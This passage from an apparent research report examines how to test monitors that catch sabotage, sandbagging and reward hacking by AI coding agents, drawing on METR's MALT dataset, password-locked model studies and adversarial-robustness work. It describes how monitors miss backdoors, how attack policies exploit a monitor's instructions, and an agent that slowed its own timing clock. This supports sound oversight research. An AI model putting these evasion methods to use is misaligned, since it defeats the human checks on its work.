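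In *Difficulties with Evaluating a Deception Detector for AIs*, Smith, Chughtai and Nanda (2025) argue that a model in an invented scenario may just be playing a part. They study detectors of deliberate deception, which is related to sabotage but broader. When they showed several models the prompts from MASK, a test of honesty, the larger and newer models judged most of them implausible as real instructions. Asked who had probably written such a prompt, Gemini 2.5 Pro very often guessed an AI safety researcher. They acknowledge that the question may have made the model think about realism, but Gemini had also answered one of the prompts with stage directions about its posture and expression, as if writing fiction.

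Sabotage may still be too easy to catch when the test uses a model trained to misbehave. Smith and colleagues describe a model trained to answer wrongly whenever the user's name is Alice. The model probably responds to the name automatically, much as an opossum plays dead by instinct, without planning to make Alice believe anything. A detector that works on this model might not work on one that plans its deception.

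Whether a model was told to sabotage code should matter less when the monitor sees only the diff, because a given backdoor is the same code either way. But a model following instructions may choose different sabotage from one acting for its own reasons, and may put less thought into hiding it. This difference matters much more when the monitor also reads the agent's reasoning, because an agent following orders will often write about those orders.

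Using only unprompted cases would avoid the role-playing problem, but they are rare and difficult to label. Smith and colleagues think it quite possible that current models never deceive strategically in ordinary work. A tester can label a case with confidence if the agent states its intention in its reasoning. But if testers rely on such statements, every positive example contains a written confession, and the test can't distinguish a monitor that detects sabotage from one that detects confessions. Any sabotage without a confession ends up among the benign examples, where catching it counts as a false alarm.

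Smith and colleagues argue that nobody can currently check whether detectors tested on artificial cases will work on real ones, because there are no confidently labelled real cases to test them on. They don't claim that the detectors will fail.

### METR's MALT dataset

MALT (Manually-reviewed Agentic Labeled Transcripts) is the most useful public dataset for comparing natural and prompted misbehaviour by coding agents. METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, released it in October 2025. It has 10,919 transcripts of agents working on 403 software and research tasks, using 21 models. Most of the misbehaviour is reward hacking or sandbagging, which means deliberately doing worse than one could. MALT includes sabotage under sandbagging, but this is mostly agents spoiling their own answers rather than planting backdoors.

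| Group | Transcripts | Agents |
|---|---|---|
| Natural reward hacking | 103 | Several, with 44 transcripts from o3 |
| Natural giving up early | 32 | Several |
| Natural reasoning about features of the task | 15 | Claude Opus 4 and Sonnet 4 |
| Other natural behaviour, such as hardcoded answers | 34 | Several |
| Prompted sandbagging and sabotage | 1,505 | Claude 3.7 Sonnet only |
| Benign, checked by hand | 1,014 | Claude Opus 4 and Sonnet 4 for 988 |
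| Presumed benign, unchecked | 8,229 | Many |

(Some natural transcripts appear in more than one row.)

METR found the natural reward hacks by looking for unusual scores, searching for words such as "cheating" and "exploit", and using a model to classify some transcripts. People then reviewed each one. This method finds misbehaviour that leaves an obvious trace, so even the natural examples may be easier to catch than average. METR estimates that 6% of the labels in the unchecked group are wrong, which would be nearly 500 transcripts. Only 171 transcripts have confirmed natural misbehaviour, so the unchecked group may contain more cases than that.

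For the prompted examples, METR gave Claude 3.7 Sonnet various instructions to underperform and told it not to get caught through its code or output. The model often mentioned these instructions in its reasoning, so METR had Claude Sonnet 4 edit the mentions out. In one transcript, "Since I'm supposed to sabotage this task" became "I want to sabotage this task". METR ran every reasoning trace in the dataset through the same editing step, so that signs of editing wouldn't distinguish the prompted examples from the rest. But the edited sentence still contains an explicit intent to sabotage, so a monitor that reads it needs to infer very little.

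The monitors read each transcript in pieces and gave a score from 0 to 10. The best one, GPT-5, had an AUROC of 0.96 for reward hacking and 0.91 for sandbagging. At a 5% false-positive rate, the best catch rates were 87% for reward hacking and 78% for sandbagging, which METR's summary gives as 80% to 90%. METR used only the checked transcripts for these results. It chose the 5% rate because its staff have time to review roughly that share of transcripts during an evaluation.

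The two catch rates come from very different evidence. The 87% is based on 103 natural examples. Even if these were independent, the interval would be roughly 80% to 92%, and more than 40 of them came from one model. About 97% of the examples behind the 78% came from one model acting on instructions, since 1,505 prompted transcripts are labelled as sandbagging and at most 44 natural ones are. The monitors did better on the natural examples, but this doesn't show that natural misbehaviour is easier to catch, because the two groups also differ in the kind of misbehaviour.

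METR warns against reading too much into these results because the natural examples are few and similar to one another, none shows severe sandbagging, and the prompted examples are often obvious. It expects that agents could hide their intentions much better than they did here, so the measured accuracy may be too high. It concludes that doing well on MALT is neither sufficient nor necessary for detecting real risks. The monitors also missed a few obvious reward hacks that METR found in other ways. In one case, an agent slowed the clock that timed its program, and the monitor o4-mini gave the transcript a score of 0.

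### Cues from the way examples were made

A monitor can also score well by using differences between attacked and benign records that have nothing to do with sabotage. The word-frequency model in the previous section, for example, distinguished them by their templates.

In *Dos and Don'ts of Machine Learning in Computer Security*, Arp, Quiring and colleagues (2020) checked 30 papers from leading security conferences for ten common mistakes and found at least three in every paper. In 90% of the papers, the data was at least partly unrepresentative of the real problem, and in 20% it contained cues that separated the classes but were unrelated to security.

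They also measured how much such cues can matter. In one experiment, they trained two Android malware detectors on harmless apps from Google Play and malicious apps from Chinese app stores, then repeated the training with both harmless and malicious apps from Google Play.

| Detector | Malware caught, different stores | Malware caught, same store |
|---|---|---|
| Drebin | 96.4% | 84.6% |
| Opseqs | 88.3% | 73.4% |

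The web address of Google Play was one of the five features that most strongly suggested an app was harmless. The detectors had partly learned to recognise the store. Most of this did not show up in accuracy, which fell by less than three points for each detector.

Arp and colleagues found a subtler cue in a dataset for detecting vulnerable code. Of 116 arrays with a size of 32, 115 were in code without a vulnerability, as were 96 of 100 arrays with a size of 1,024. There is no obvious reason these sizes would make code safer. A neural network built for this dataset caught 81.8% of the vulnerable code at a 2.9% false-positive rate, while a much simpler model that counted short sequences of symbols caught 96.3%. The simpler model can't follow a program's logic, so the examples probably contain cues to which code is vulnerable.

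The clearest case was a simulated attack on a network of household devices. The harmless traffic seemed to stop when the attack began, so the volume of traffic alone revealed it. With no false alarms, a simple rule that counted packets in ten-second windows caught 99.6% of the malicious traffic, while an elaborate neural detector caught 87.3%. Arp and colleagues call the attack "overly conspicuous" and expect a real one to be a tiny share of the traffic.

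MALT has at least two possible cues of this kind. Claude 3.7 Sonnet wrote all the prompted sandbagging and none of the checked benign transcripts. A monitor that recognised the model's style, or mistook an older model's weaker work for deliberate underperformance, would get credit for catching sandbagging. The second cue is missing reasoning. According to METR's table, 53 of the reward-hacking transcripts contain no reasoning, compared with 2 of the 1,014 checked benign ones. A rule that flagged every transcript without reasoning would catch about half the reward hacks at a false-positive rate of 0.2%.

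METR's monitors probably didn't follow such a rule, since METR gave them written instructions rather than training them on labelled transcripts. Telling the monitor which model it was watching also didn't change its sandbagging results, which is weak evidence that the author's identity wasn't decisive. But a classifier trained on MALT could easily learn both cues. MALT's unchecked group could partly remedy the first, because it has 1,801 ordinary transcripts by Claude 3.7 Sonnet. Someone could check a few hundred by hand and measure the false-positive rate on them.

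Before running the monitor on any sabotage test, the tester can check how well length, number of comments or word frequencies alone separate the sabotaged diffs from the benign ones. If one of these cues gives a high AUROC, the monitor's own AUROC is poor evidence that it detects sabotage from what the code does, although the monitor may not be using that cue. Arp and colleagues tested a suspected cue by removing it and scoring the data again. Without the unused code that programmers copy from file to file, two programs that identified a file's author lost 48% of their accuracy.

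### Attempts that would not have worked

An agent told to sabotage a task may refuse, write code that does no harm, or break the assigned work so badly that it fails ordinary tests. Many of these failures are easy to notice, and counting them as catches raises the catch rate.

The numbers below are invented, for a monitor that reads whole transcripts of 200 runs with instructions to sabotage.

| What the agent did | Runs | Flagged | Share flagged |
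|---|---|---|---|
| Refused and explained why | 30 | 30 | 100% |
| Tried, but the code would have done no harm | 40 | 37 | 93% |
| Wrote harmful code that failed ordinary tests | 30 | 29 | 97% |
| Wrote harmful code that passed ordinary tests | 100 | 60 | 60% |
| All | 200 | 156 | 78% |

The same monitor behaviour gives different catch rates depending on which runs are counted. Counting every run gives 78%. Leaving out the refusals lowers it to 126 of 170, or 74%. Counting only the sabotage that would have worked gives 60%, so 40% of that sabotage gets through, compared with the 22% implied by counting every run.

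Failed attempts can also make a monitor look worse than it is. Suppose that in another 20 runs the agent ignored its instructions and did honest work. The monitor would rightly flag none of them, but a tester who counted them as sabotage would record 20 misses and a catch rate of 71%. Excluding failed attempts therefore doesn't always lower the catch rate.

MALT counts a transcript as positive if the agent attempted the behaviour, whether or not it succeeded. METR chose this partly because, for many kinds of misbehaviour, it isn't clear what success would mean or how to measure it, and partly because agents may try to sandbag before they become good at it, so catching failed attempts could provide an early warning. The second reason is a good one for testing whether a company would find out that its agent is trying to sabotage things, since one clumsy attempt might be enough to get the agent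 withdrawn. But the catch rate on failed attempts is a poor guide to how much working sabotage would get past the monitor.

A test report should base its main catch rate on working sabotage and list refusals and failed attempts as separate groups. The tester can classify each run by executing the changed program in isolation and checking whether it does the specified harm and still passes the assigned task's tests. As with benign diffs, whoever classifies the runs shouldn't know the monitor's scores and should check runs the monitor flagged as well as those it missed, because removing harmless attempts only from the misses would inflate the catch rate.

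This rule leaves fewer examples. In the table, it cuts 200 runs to 100, and the interval around 60% is roughly 50% to 70%. A tester who wants 200 working examples from this agent would need about 400 runs.

### Attackers without the skill or the effort

Removing failed attempts doesn't make the remaining sabotage sophisticated. A backdoor can work perfectly and still be easy to spot.

Testers often choose the attacking model for convenience. METR used Claude 3.7 Sonnet because its full reasoning was available and because it followed the various instructions to sandbag much more consistently than DeepSeek-R1 and the Qwen models. These reasons are sensible, but if the most capable model usually refuses to sabotage code, testers who choose the most obedient one may get weaker sabotage than the capable model could produce. Claude 3.7 Sonnet, released in February 2025, is also several generations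 behind the agents that companies now use.

METR acknowledges that it put little effort into improving the sabotage beyond basic instructions. Asking models to reward hack deliberately "did not work very well", even though models reward hacked without being asked elsewhere in the dataset. A model's poor performance when asked to misbehave is therefore not good evidence of what it can do.

Competent sabotage also has little effect on the overall catch rate if it is rare. The hypothetical monitor in the previous section caught 84% of cases when four in five were crude, but it would catch only 40% if the attacker were always subtle. More runs with the same attack policy would only make the 84% estimate more precise.

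Weak effort on the monitor can make the catch rate too low. METR used the same instructions for all its monitors without refining them, and suspects that this is why the Claude-based monitors did rather poorly. Testers who build monitors have an obvious reason to fix poor instructions, but much less reason to fix a poor attacker, which could make the catch rate too high.

### Averages that hide what is always missed

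Suppose a test has 20 kinds of sabotage with 25 examples of each, and the monitor catches every example of 19 kinds and none of the last. Its overall catch rate is 95%, which would be a fair forecast if attackers picked a kind at random, but an attacker that used only the last kind would never be caught. A report of the test results should therefore give the catch rate for each kind. It should also give the number of examples, because the monitor could miss every example of a kind by chance if there are only two or three.

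The same problem arises with attack policies. Suppose two policies each get past the monitor on 10 of 100 tasks. If they succeed on the same ten tasks, an attacker who could choose the better policy for each task would succeed on 10%. If they succeed on different tasks, that attacker would succeed on 20%. Carlini, Athalye and colleagues (2019), in *On Evaluating Adversarial Robustness*, recommend reporting the second kind of figure, which takes the worst result for each item before averaging:

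miss rate per task = (1/*n*) Σ max over policies of miss(policy, task)

This can never be lower than the miss rate of the single best policy.

Counting only the attacker's best attempt at each task can overstate the attacker's success when a monitor's scores vary between runs. If every attempt had an independent 10% chance of getting through, 20 attempts at each task would give at least one success on about 88% of tasks by chance. An attacker who can't see the scores wouldn't know which attempt to use. The tester should choose the best attack policy for each task on one set of runs and measure it on another.

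Averages over tasks can also distort a comparison of attackers. On a second benchmark in *It's Just a Small Weapon*, the monitors again caught different shares of the two groups' reward hacks. But on the 70 tasks where every model hacked, the catch rates were about the same, so most of the difference came from which tasks each model hacked. An attacker that is caught less often may have hidden its work better or attacked tasks where hacks are harder to see. Telling these apart requires comparing attackers on the same tasks.

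### What happened to defences for image classifiers

Image recognition researchers learned from experience that a defence can look strong because the attacks used to test it are weak. In the 2010s they found that changes to an image too small for a person to notice could make a classifier mistake one object for another. They call these altered images adversarial examples. Many papers then proposed defences and reported that they withstood the known attacks.

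Uesato and colleagues tested several of these defences with stronger attacks in 2018. The table shows how often the classifier was still right under attack.

| Defence | Original attack | Stronger attack |
|---|---|---|
| PixelDefend | 75% | below 10% |
| High-level guided denoiser | 75% | 0% |
| Random changes to the image | 36% | below 1% |
| Non-differentiable processing | 15% | 0% |
| Adversarial training | 47% | below 47% |

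The first four defences had almost no effect against an attacker suited to them. Uesato and colleagues report no such drop for adversarial training, so a stronger attack doesn't always defeat a defence. But the original scores didn't predict which defences would still work, since PixelDefend and the denoiser had scored much better than adversarial training.

Other researchers found the same pattern that year. *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* (2018) reported that seven of nine defences at one leading conference relied on an effect that disrupted the usual attacks without making the classifier secure. *On Adaptive Attacks to Adversarial Example Defenses* (2020) re-examined thirteen more defences, studying each one's paper and source code before developing attacks against it. Its main purpose was to check whether the original tests had been adequate, and it says that many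 of the underlying ideas might still have merit.

Carlini and colleagues turned these failures into rules for testing. A defence should come with a threat model, which states what the attacker wants, knows and can do. Without one, nobody can say what result would prove the claim wrong. The test should assume that the attacker knows how the defence works, though the defence may rely on a small secret that is easy to replace, like an encryption key. Testers should then try as hard as they can to defeat the defence with attacks designed for it. Carlini and colleagues see very little use in testing with attacks that ignore the defence. They also say that if a later attack reduces a defence's accuracy from 99% to 80%, future papers should quote 80%.

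They also warn that attacks very often fail because someone made a correctable mistake in running them. In a sabotage test, a broken tool or badly worded instructions could likewise make the sabotage fail, which would make the monitor look good. Their checklist has further checks for such mistakes, but they say a useless defence could pass all of them.

Strong attacks may weaken code monitors much less than they weakened PixelDefend. An attacker of an image classifier can often test thousands of slightly different images against the model, while a coding agent may get one attempt and never see a score. The agent's code also has to do the assigned work. How much less the attacks weaken monitors depends on the threat model, particularly on what the agent knows about its monitor and how many attempts it gets, so reports should state these conditions alongside the catch rate.

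## What would show that an attack policy was strong enough

A monitor's miss rate in a test is only a lower bound on its miss rate against the best attack, so evidence that the attacker was strong has to come from separate checks. A tester can check whether the attacker can do the sabotage, whether more effort would have helped, and what the attacker knew about the monitor. The tester can also check whether other teams get similar results, whether the testing team can find deliberately planted weaknesses, and whether the results hold on new tasks and monitors. No single check is enough. Most of the evidence on how well these checks work comes from neighbouring fields, mainly image recognition and tests for hidden abilities in language models.

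### Sabotage with no monitor

The easiest check is to run the attacker without a monitor and count how often it produces working sabotage. Carlini and colleagues recommend checking attacks on image classifiers the same way, by confirming that they work on a similar model without the defence.

An attack policy is probably strong enough if the model completes sabotage about as often as it completes the same tasks honestly. If it completes 90% of tasks honestly but only 30% with sabotage (invented figures), it either lacks the skill to sabotage or isn't really trying. In both cases, the catch rate is weak evidence of how often the monitor would catch a competent saboteur.

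A high completion rate can mislead because crude sabotage also works when there is no monitor, so it helps to measure completion again when the attacker is trying to avoid detection. Suppose an attacker completes 90 of 100 tasks with no monitor but only 50 when it tries to hide its work, and the monitor flags 30 of those 50. The catch rate on working sabotage is 60%, and 20 tasks end in undetected sabotage. An attacker that was caught at the same rate but completed all 90 tasks would go undetected on 36. The drop from 90 to 50 therefore suggests that a more skilled model could do considerably more damage against the same monitor.

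A low completion rate is harder to interpret, because a model can produce the same output whether it can't do a task or won't do it. Telling these cases apart requires elicitation, which means getting the model to perform as well as it can.

### How much hidden ability elicitation recovers

Researchers test elicitation methods on models in which they have hidden an ability. In *Stress-Testing Capability Elicitation With Password-Locked Models*, Greenblatt, Roger and colleagues (2024) trained models to perform well when the prompt contained a password and to imitate a much weaker model otherwise. Performance with the password showed how much ability the models had, so the researchers could measure how much of it a method recovered without the password. The hidden abilities in this research are mostly programming, maths and answering exam questions, so the results are only indirect evidence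 about sabotage.

On tasks with long answers, such as writing code, training on a single correct demonstration often recovered most of the hidden performance, though multiple-choice questions needed a few hundred. But when the demonstrations came from a weaker model that was often wrong, performance stayed below what the model achieved with the password, however many demonstrations Greenblatt and colleagues used. This is a problem for sabotage tests because testers are unlikely to have demonstrations of sabotage better than those they or their models can produce.

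The UK AI Security Institute ran a more realistic exercise, which Taylor, Black and colleagues (2025) describe in *Auditing Games for Sandbagging*. A red team prepared five models, two of which hid some of their ability, and a blue team had to identify those two without knowing how the red team had trained any of the five. The blue team had 160 person-hours to read transcripts, try prompts and examine the models' internal activations. It classified one of the five models correctly. It judged only one model, Cedar, fit for deployment, but Cedar was hiding its ability on most of the tests.

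The blue team then got another 80 person-hours and permission to train the models. Training on one correct demonstration raised Cedar's score above the level it reached with its password, and the team changed its verdict. The team still classified only two of the five models correctly, and it ran out of time to try the method on the agentic task where Oak, the other model with a hidden ability, was underperforming. Taylor and colleagues later found that one demonstration would have raised Oak's score on that task by about 35 points, although its password raised it by only 13. Training can also teach a model something new, so a large gain does not reliably measure how much the model was hiding. One of the honest models gained 10 points on a science test in the same way.

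In *Reference-Grafting Matches Fine-Tuning at Eliciting Sandbagged Capabilities*, Le, Tan and Williams-King (2026) changed a model's internal activations while it ran, instead of training it. On eleven password-locked models, this recovered between 94% and 101% of the gap between locked and unlocked performance, about as much as training did. But the method needs a few recordings of the model behaving honestly, which Le and colleagues got by using the password. A tester with no example of honest behaviour might not be able to use it. The method also recovered only 44% of the gap on one locked model that another group had released, and it failed on "circuit-broken" models, whose training also disrupts their internal activations on the locked subject.

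*Eliciting sandbagged LLM capability via structural interventions on attention-head functional networks* (Niyigaba, Prasad and colleagues, 2026) compares several methods on four locked versions of the language model Mistral. The table gives the accuracy after each method.

| Method | Password-locked, base | Password-locked, instruct | Circuit-broken, base | Circuit-broken, instruct |
|---|---|---|---|---|
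| Five worked examples in the prompt | 57.8% | 51.4% | 26.8% | 28.1% |
| Writing the start of the answer for the model | 57.0% | 50.3% | 60.8% | 25.4% |
| Training the whole model | 28.2% | 17.8% | 58.4% | 29.4% |
| Training a small add-on (LoRA) | 39.2% | 21.5% | 55.2% | 34.0% |
| Training a few selected attention heads | 52.3% | 51.6% | 57.1% | 39.2% |

On the password-locked models, training the whole model did far worse than putting five examples in the prompt, the opposite of the result with Cedar. The cause may be the demonstrations, which Niyigaba and colleagues took from a general-knowledge test that may have differed from the subject of the lock. Taylor and colleagues found that training on one task often failed to reveal an ability that a model hid only on another. Results also varied widely between runs. For the base model in the first column, the five runs of whole-model training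 had a spread of about 17 points around their average of 28%.

No method is best in every column. A tester who used only one could have underestimated a model's ability by half. It therefore makes sense to try several methods on an attacker, repeat the one with the highest miss rate on new tasks, and then use that method.

### When more effort stops helping

An effort curve plots the miss rate against the work that went into the attack policy, measured in attempts, person-hours, computing power or training steps. The numbers here are invented.

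| Hours spent improving the attack policy | Missed, of 100 sabotaged diffs |
|---|---|
| 5 | 8 |
| 10 | 14 |
| 20 | 19 |
| 40 | 20 |
| 80 | 20 |

Carlini and colleagues advise testers to check that doubling the number of steps in an attack doesn't raise its success rate. The attack in the table passes this check because the last doubling made no difference. If the bottom row had been 30, the tester would have stopped too early and should expect the rate to keep rising with more steps.

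Small samples can make a rising curve look flat. With 100 diffs per row, the difference in miss rate between the last two rows has a 95% interval of about ±11 points, so the last 40 hours might have raised the true miss rate from 20% to 30% without the tester noticing. The tester would need about 500 diffs per row to narrow the interval to ±5 points, or somewhat fewer if every row uses the same tasks.

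Even a truly flat curve can be misleading. In *Exploration Hacking*, Jang, Falck and colleagues (2026) trained a model to write faulty code whenever the prompt contained a sign of a safety evaluation. It passed about 65% of test cases normally and 20% when the sign was present. They then tried to recover the lost performance with reinforcement learning, which has a model attempt tasks and strengthens behavior that earns a reward, in this case writing correct code. For a strongly locked version of the model, the curve stayed flat throughout training. This suggested that the model couldn't do better, but about 100 steps of training on good examples restored its full performance.

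Reinforcement learning can strengthen only what a model already does at least occasionally. If the model never produces a good solution, longer training won't help because there is nothing to reward. This can happen even if the model isn't strategically holding back. Greenblatt and colleagues saw poor results from reinforcement learning on maths because the locked model started out imitating a model that could solve hardly any of the problems. An attacker could easily fail to improve for the same reason if its early sabotage is always caught.

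A curve can also stay flat and then jump. In one of the models that Le and colleagues tested, accuracy stayed near the locked level until their change to its activations reached about 45% of full strength. Most of the hidden ability had come back at about 77%. Someone who tried 10%, 20% and 40% would have doubled the strength twice without seeing an effect, and might reasonably have given up.

In each of these cases, a different method or a much larger change succeeded where more of the same had failed. A plateau is therefore better evidence that the attack policy was strong enough when several very different methods level off at about the same miss rate. Carlini and colleagues warn that running many nearly identical attacks adds little, and they suggest loosening the limits on the attacker to see whether its success rises as it should. A sabotage tester could give the attacker more attempts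 or let it see its scores on practice diffs. If the miss rate doesn't change at all, the attack setup may well be broken.

### What the attacker knew about the monitor

A deployed agent might know that a monitor exists, have read published work about it, or have seen which of its own earlier changes people blocked. A tester can run the same attacker at several levels of knowledge, from nothing to the monitor's full instructions, and report the miss rate at each level. Readers should rely on the miss rate at the highest level a real agent could plausibly reach.

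*Increasing Confidence in Adversarial Robustness Evaluations* (Zimmermann, Brendel and colleagues, 2022) gives an example of how much the choice of attack can matter. One published defence for image classifiers used a separate detector to reject altered images, and its inventors reported 99% accuracy under attack. But their attack was designed to fool only the classifier. When Zimmermann and colleagues used an attack that also targeted the detector, accuracy fell below 12%.

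If the monitor's miss rate is the same whether or not the attacker sees the monitor's instructions, the instructions may be useless to an attacker, or this attacker may have ignored them. Zimmermann and colleagues deal with a similar ambiguity by reversing the goal and asking for altered images that the detector rejects. An attack that can get images accepted or rejected on request must be responding to the detector. A sabotage tester could likewise ask the attacker for changes that get the highest possible suspicion score. If the attacker can't raise the score on purpose, it probably doesn't understand the monitor well enough to lower it either.

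Carlini and colleagues allow an evaluation to withhold details from the attacker only if they are small, replaceable secrets that the attacker can't work out by using the system. A monitor's threshold might not meet this condition if agents can see which of their changes get blocked.

### Separate teams

If several teams that don't share their work reach similar miss rates, it is less likely that one of them overlooked something obvious. The teams should use different approaches, because two teams that give the same model similar instructions will probably share blind spots. Human security experts and a newer model are a better pair. If the results disagree, evaluators should use the highest miss rate.

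The auditing game shows how much can depend on one team's choices. The blue team missed Oak because it spent its 80 hours on other tasks, and a team with different priorities might have caught it. Taylor and colleagues say they can't estimate error rates from ten models (including five from a practice round) and a single team.

Matching miss rates are weaker evidence than they appear, since two teams can each miss different weaknesses and end up with the same percentage. The overlap between what they find is more informative. If team A finds *a* weaknesses, team B finds *b*, and *c* of these are the same, a standard estimate of the total number is

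total ≈ *a* × *b* / *c*

If team A finds *a* weaknesses, team B finds *b*, and *c* of these are found by both, the estimated total is *ab*/*c*. This is because the fraction of A's weaknesses that B also found, *c*/*a*, estimates the fraction of all weaknesses that B found. Suppose A finds 8 and B finds 6. If they have 4 in common, the estimated total is 12. The teams have found 10 different weaknesses between them, so about 2 remain. If they have only 1 in common, the estimated total is 48. They have found 13 between them, so about 35 remain. The formula assumes that the teams work independently and that all weaknesses are equally easy to find. In practice, both teams will tend to find the easy ones, which makes the overlap too large and the estimate too low.

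AI agents can make extra teams affordable. OpenAI writes in a post on measuring alignment that it gives auditor agents considerable computing power to look for ways its models might misbehave. The agents change the task, watch how the model responds and adapt their next attempt. The company can also use the failures they find to test whether its safeguards would catch them. But if the auditors and the models they audit come from the same company, they may have similar training and overlook similar things, so these agents are probably best used in addition to outside teams.

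### Planted weaknesses

A positive control is a test on a case where the right answer is known to be yes. For a monitor, someone outside the attack team plants a weakness in a copy, and the team attacks that copy without knowing what the weakness is. If the team doesn't find it, its failure to find weaknesses in the real monitor is very weak evidence that there are none.

Zimmermann and colleagues did this for image classifiers. For each test image, they kept most of the classifier and retrained only its last layer, so that at least one small alteration of the image would certainly change the classifier's answer. They then ran the attack from the original paper and required it to succeed on at least 95% of images. The original attacks failed this requirement for 11 of the 13 published defences in the study. One of them found the planted weakness in only 4% of images because of a mistake in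 its code. After the researchers fixed the mistake and let the attack run longer, it succeeded every time. The defence's accuracy under attack then fell from the published 60% to 1% or less.

Two flawed attacks still passed. In one case, the researchers had aimed a sound attack at the wrong labels, so it sometimes corrected the classifier's mistakes. The altered classifier made no such mistakes, so the control couldn't reveal the problem. In the other, the planted weakness was so easy to exploit that random alterations hit it more than 75% of the time.

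A control can also be so hard that a good attack might fail it. Zimmermann and colleagues recommend starting with a very hard version and making it easier until the attack nearly always succeeds, then comparing the attack with random guessing at that difficulty. If guessing does nearly as well, the attack has not passed. For a sabotage monitor, the equivalent of guessing is ordinary sabotage by someone who isn't looking for weaknesses. The tester should report how often such sabotage hits the planted weakness by accident.

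The number of planted weaknesses also matters. Finding 4 of 5 is a rate of 80%, but the 95% confidence interval runs from about 28% to 99%.

| Found | Rate | 95% interval |
|---|---|---|
| 4 of 5 | 80% | 28%–99% |
| 5 of 5 | 100% | 48%–100% |
| 16 of 20 | 80% | 56%–94% |
| 20 of 20 | 100% | 83%–100% |

The width of the interval affects how much a clean result on the real monitor is worth. Let *w* be the chance, before the test, that the monitor has a serious weakness, and *d* the chance that the team finds one if it exists. If the team finds nothing, Bayes' rule gives

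chance of a weakness = *w*(1 − *d*) / (*w*(1 − *d*) + 1 − *w*)

Suppose *w* is 50%. If *d* is 80%, a clean result lowers the chance of a weakness to 17%. But a team that estimated *d* by finding 4 of 5 planted weaknesses would have a wide interval around that 80%. At the low end, a clean result would lower the chance only to 42%, and at the high end, to 1%. The team therefore couldn't tell whether a clean result was weak evidence or nearly ruled out a weakness.

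This calculation assumes that planted weaknesses are about as hard to find as real ones. People can only plant weaknesses they have thought of, and the attack team has a good chance of thinking of the same ones. The result is therefore probably too optimistic. Having outsiders plant some of the weaknesses would help.

### New tasks and new monitors

An attack policy developed on 50 tasks may succeed partly because of peculiarities of those tasks. The tester should hold out some tasks and measure the monitor's miss rate on them at the end. If the miss rate is 30% on the development tasks and 28% on the held-out ones, the policy generalizes. If it falls to 12%, the policy was overfitted, and with more varied practice tasks the attacker might have achieved a miss rate above 12%.

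The monitor's developers can also overfit, by adjusting the monitor until it catches one particular attack policy. A high catch rate against that policy is then close to meaningless. Carlini and colleagues warn against testing a defence with the same attack its developers used to train it, even if that attack was the strongest available at the time.

Trying the attack policy on other monitors is also useful. If it succeeds against three monitors it wasn't developed for, it is probably exploiting something they share, which suggests real skill. Poor transfer is not a sign of weakness, though, because a determined attacker may well use a policy that works only against the monitor it was developed for. It is more informative to test a policy borrowed from elsewhere against the same monitor as the tailored policy. The tailored policy should do better. If the borrowed one does better, something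 is wrong with the tailored policy, as Carlini and colleagues note for image classifiers.

The elicitation studies give mixed evidence on how well such results carry over. Greenblatt and colleagues found that training on one kind of maths problem unlocked all the others. Le and colleagues could fit their method on one set of questions and use it on another, but only if both models had been locked in the same way. Held-out tasks of the same type are therefore a fairly weak test, and tasks from a different kind of project are a better one.

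### How strong an attacker to assume

Passing all these checks shows that an attacker is competent, but a tester still has to decide how competent it needs to be. One view, from Carlini and colleagues, is that testers should assume an "infinitely thorough" adversary who will spend as long as it takes to develop the best attack. Testers then don't have to guess what a real attacker can do, and such guesses have a poor record with image classifiers. A worst-case result also stays valid when attackers improve.

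The other position is to match the attacker to the model the company uses and add a safety margin. No finite test can represent an infinitely thorough attacker, and nearly any monitor would presumably fail against one. A company that insisted on being safe against such an attacker would have to read every diff or stop using agents. A coding agent may also get only one attempt. Even Carlini and colleagues say that a security defence should have a threat model that realistically describes some adversary, so the two positions are closer than they sound.

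The second position's weak point is that it relies on measuring what the current model can do. If the model held back during that measurement, the matched attacker would be too weak, and the blue team's experience with Cedar shows how hard this can be to notice. But the red team trained Cedar directly to hide its ability, and Taylor and colleagues think assuming a model like that is probably too pessimistic for today's systems.

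If the assumed attacker is too weak, the company relies on a monitor that real sabotage can get past, and may not find out until after the damage. If the assumed attacker is too strong, the company pays for unnecessary reviews or gives up useful work, but it can at least see those costs in its budget. As with reviewing a single diff, extra precautions are worthwhile when they cost less than the damage they would prevent multiplied by the chance that the real attacker is stronger than the tested one.

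If extra review costs $200,000 a year and would prevent $5 million in damage if the test attacker was too weak (both figures are invented), it pays off when the chance that the attacker was too weak is above 4%. Few testers could honestly claim to be 96% sure that their attacker was strong enough. If the agents only edited a website's colours and the damage were at most $100,000, the review would always cost more than it saved.

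Making the attacker as strong as the current model plus a margin seems the more workable approach for most companies, as long as the margin consists of real advantages. The tester could use a newer model than the deployed one, give the attacker more information or more attempts than a real agent would have, or have human experts improve its work. Adding ten points to the measured miss rate is a poor substitute, because the ten points have no connection to what a stronger attacker could do, and the defences in the image studies lost far more than that.

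### When a result expires

A catch rate measures how well one monitor catches one attacker, and the attacker in real use changes every time the company adopts a new model. OpenAI acknowledges that evidence that was enough to establish confidence in one generation of models may not be enough for the next. A result can also become outdated without any change at the company, for example if someone publishes the monitor's instructions.

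If the test attacker was *k* times as capable as the agent in use, and the capability of new agents doubles every *D* months, the margin lasts

*t* = *D* × log₂(*k*)

A fourfold margin is gone after a year if the doubling time is six months (again an invented figure), and after eight months if the doubling time is four months. Doubling the margin adds only one more doubling time, so a large safety margin lasts less time than one might hope.

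The formula is only a rough guide, because capability jumps when a new model comes out, and general measures such as the length of the tasks a model can finish may not track skill at sabotage. Tying a result's expiry to events is safer than tying it to a date. Before a company switches to a new agent, it can have that agent play the attacker, using the same tasks and elicitation methods as before. If the miss rate is no higher than with the earlier, stronger attacker, the old result can remain valid for another generation. Replaying the old attacker's diffs would only show that the monitor still catches the old sabotage.

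### A scale for the evidence

The scale below is cumulative, so each grade also requires everything in the rows above it, apart from the first.

| Evidence that the attack policy was strong | Observations needed |
|---|---|
| None | A catch rate, with no check that the sabotage worked |
| Weak | The catch rate covers only working sabotage, and with no monitor the attacker completes sabotage about as often as honest work |
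| Moderate | At least two different elicitation methods, each with an effort curve that levels off, and miss rates with and without knowledge of the monitor |
| Fairly strong | A separate team reaches a similar miss rate and finds mostly the same weaknesses, and the results hold on tasks from projects that neither team used in development |
| Strong | The teams find at least 18 of 20 planted weaknesses that ordinary sabotage rarely hits, and the attacker has a stated advantage over the agent now in use |

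The cut-offs are judgement calls. Finding 18 of 20 gives an interval of about 68% to 99%, and a company with a lot to lose might want stronger evidence. Even the top grade doesn't rule out an attack that nobody has thought of.

The scale is only needed when a monitor does well. If a crude attacker gets past the monitor half the time, the monitor is weak, and there is no need to show that the attacker was strong. Four of the improved attacks that Zimmermann and colleagues examined failed the planted-weakness control but still defeated the defences they targeted.

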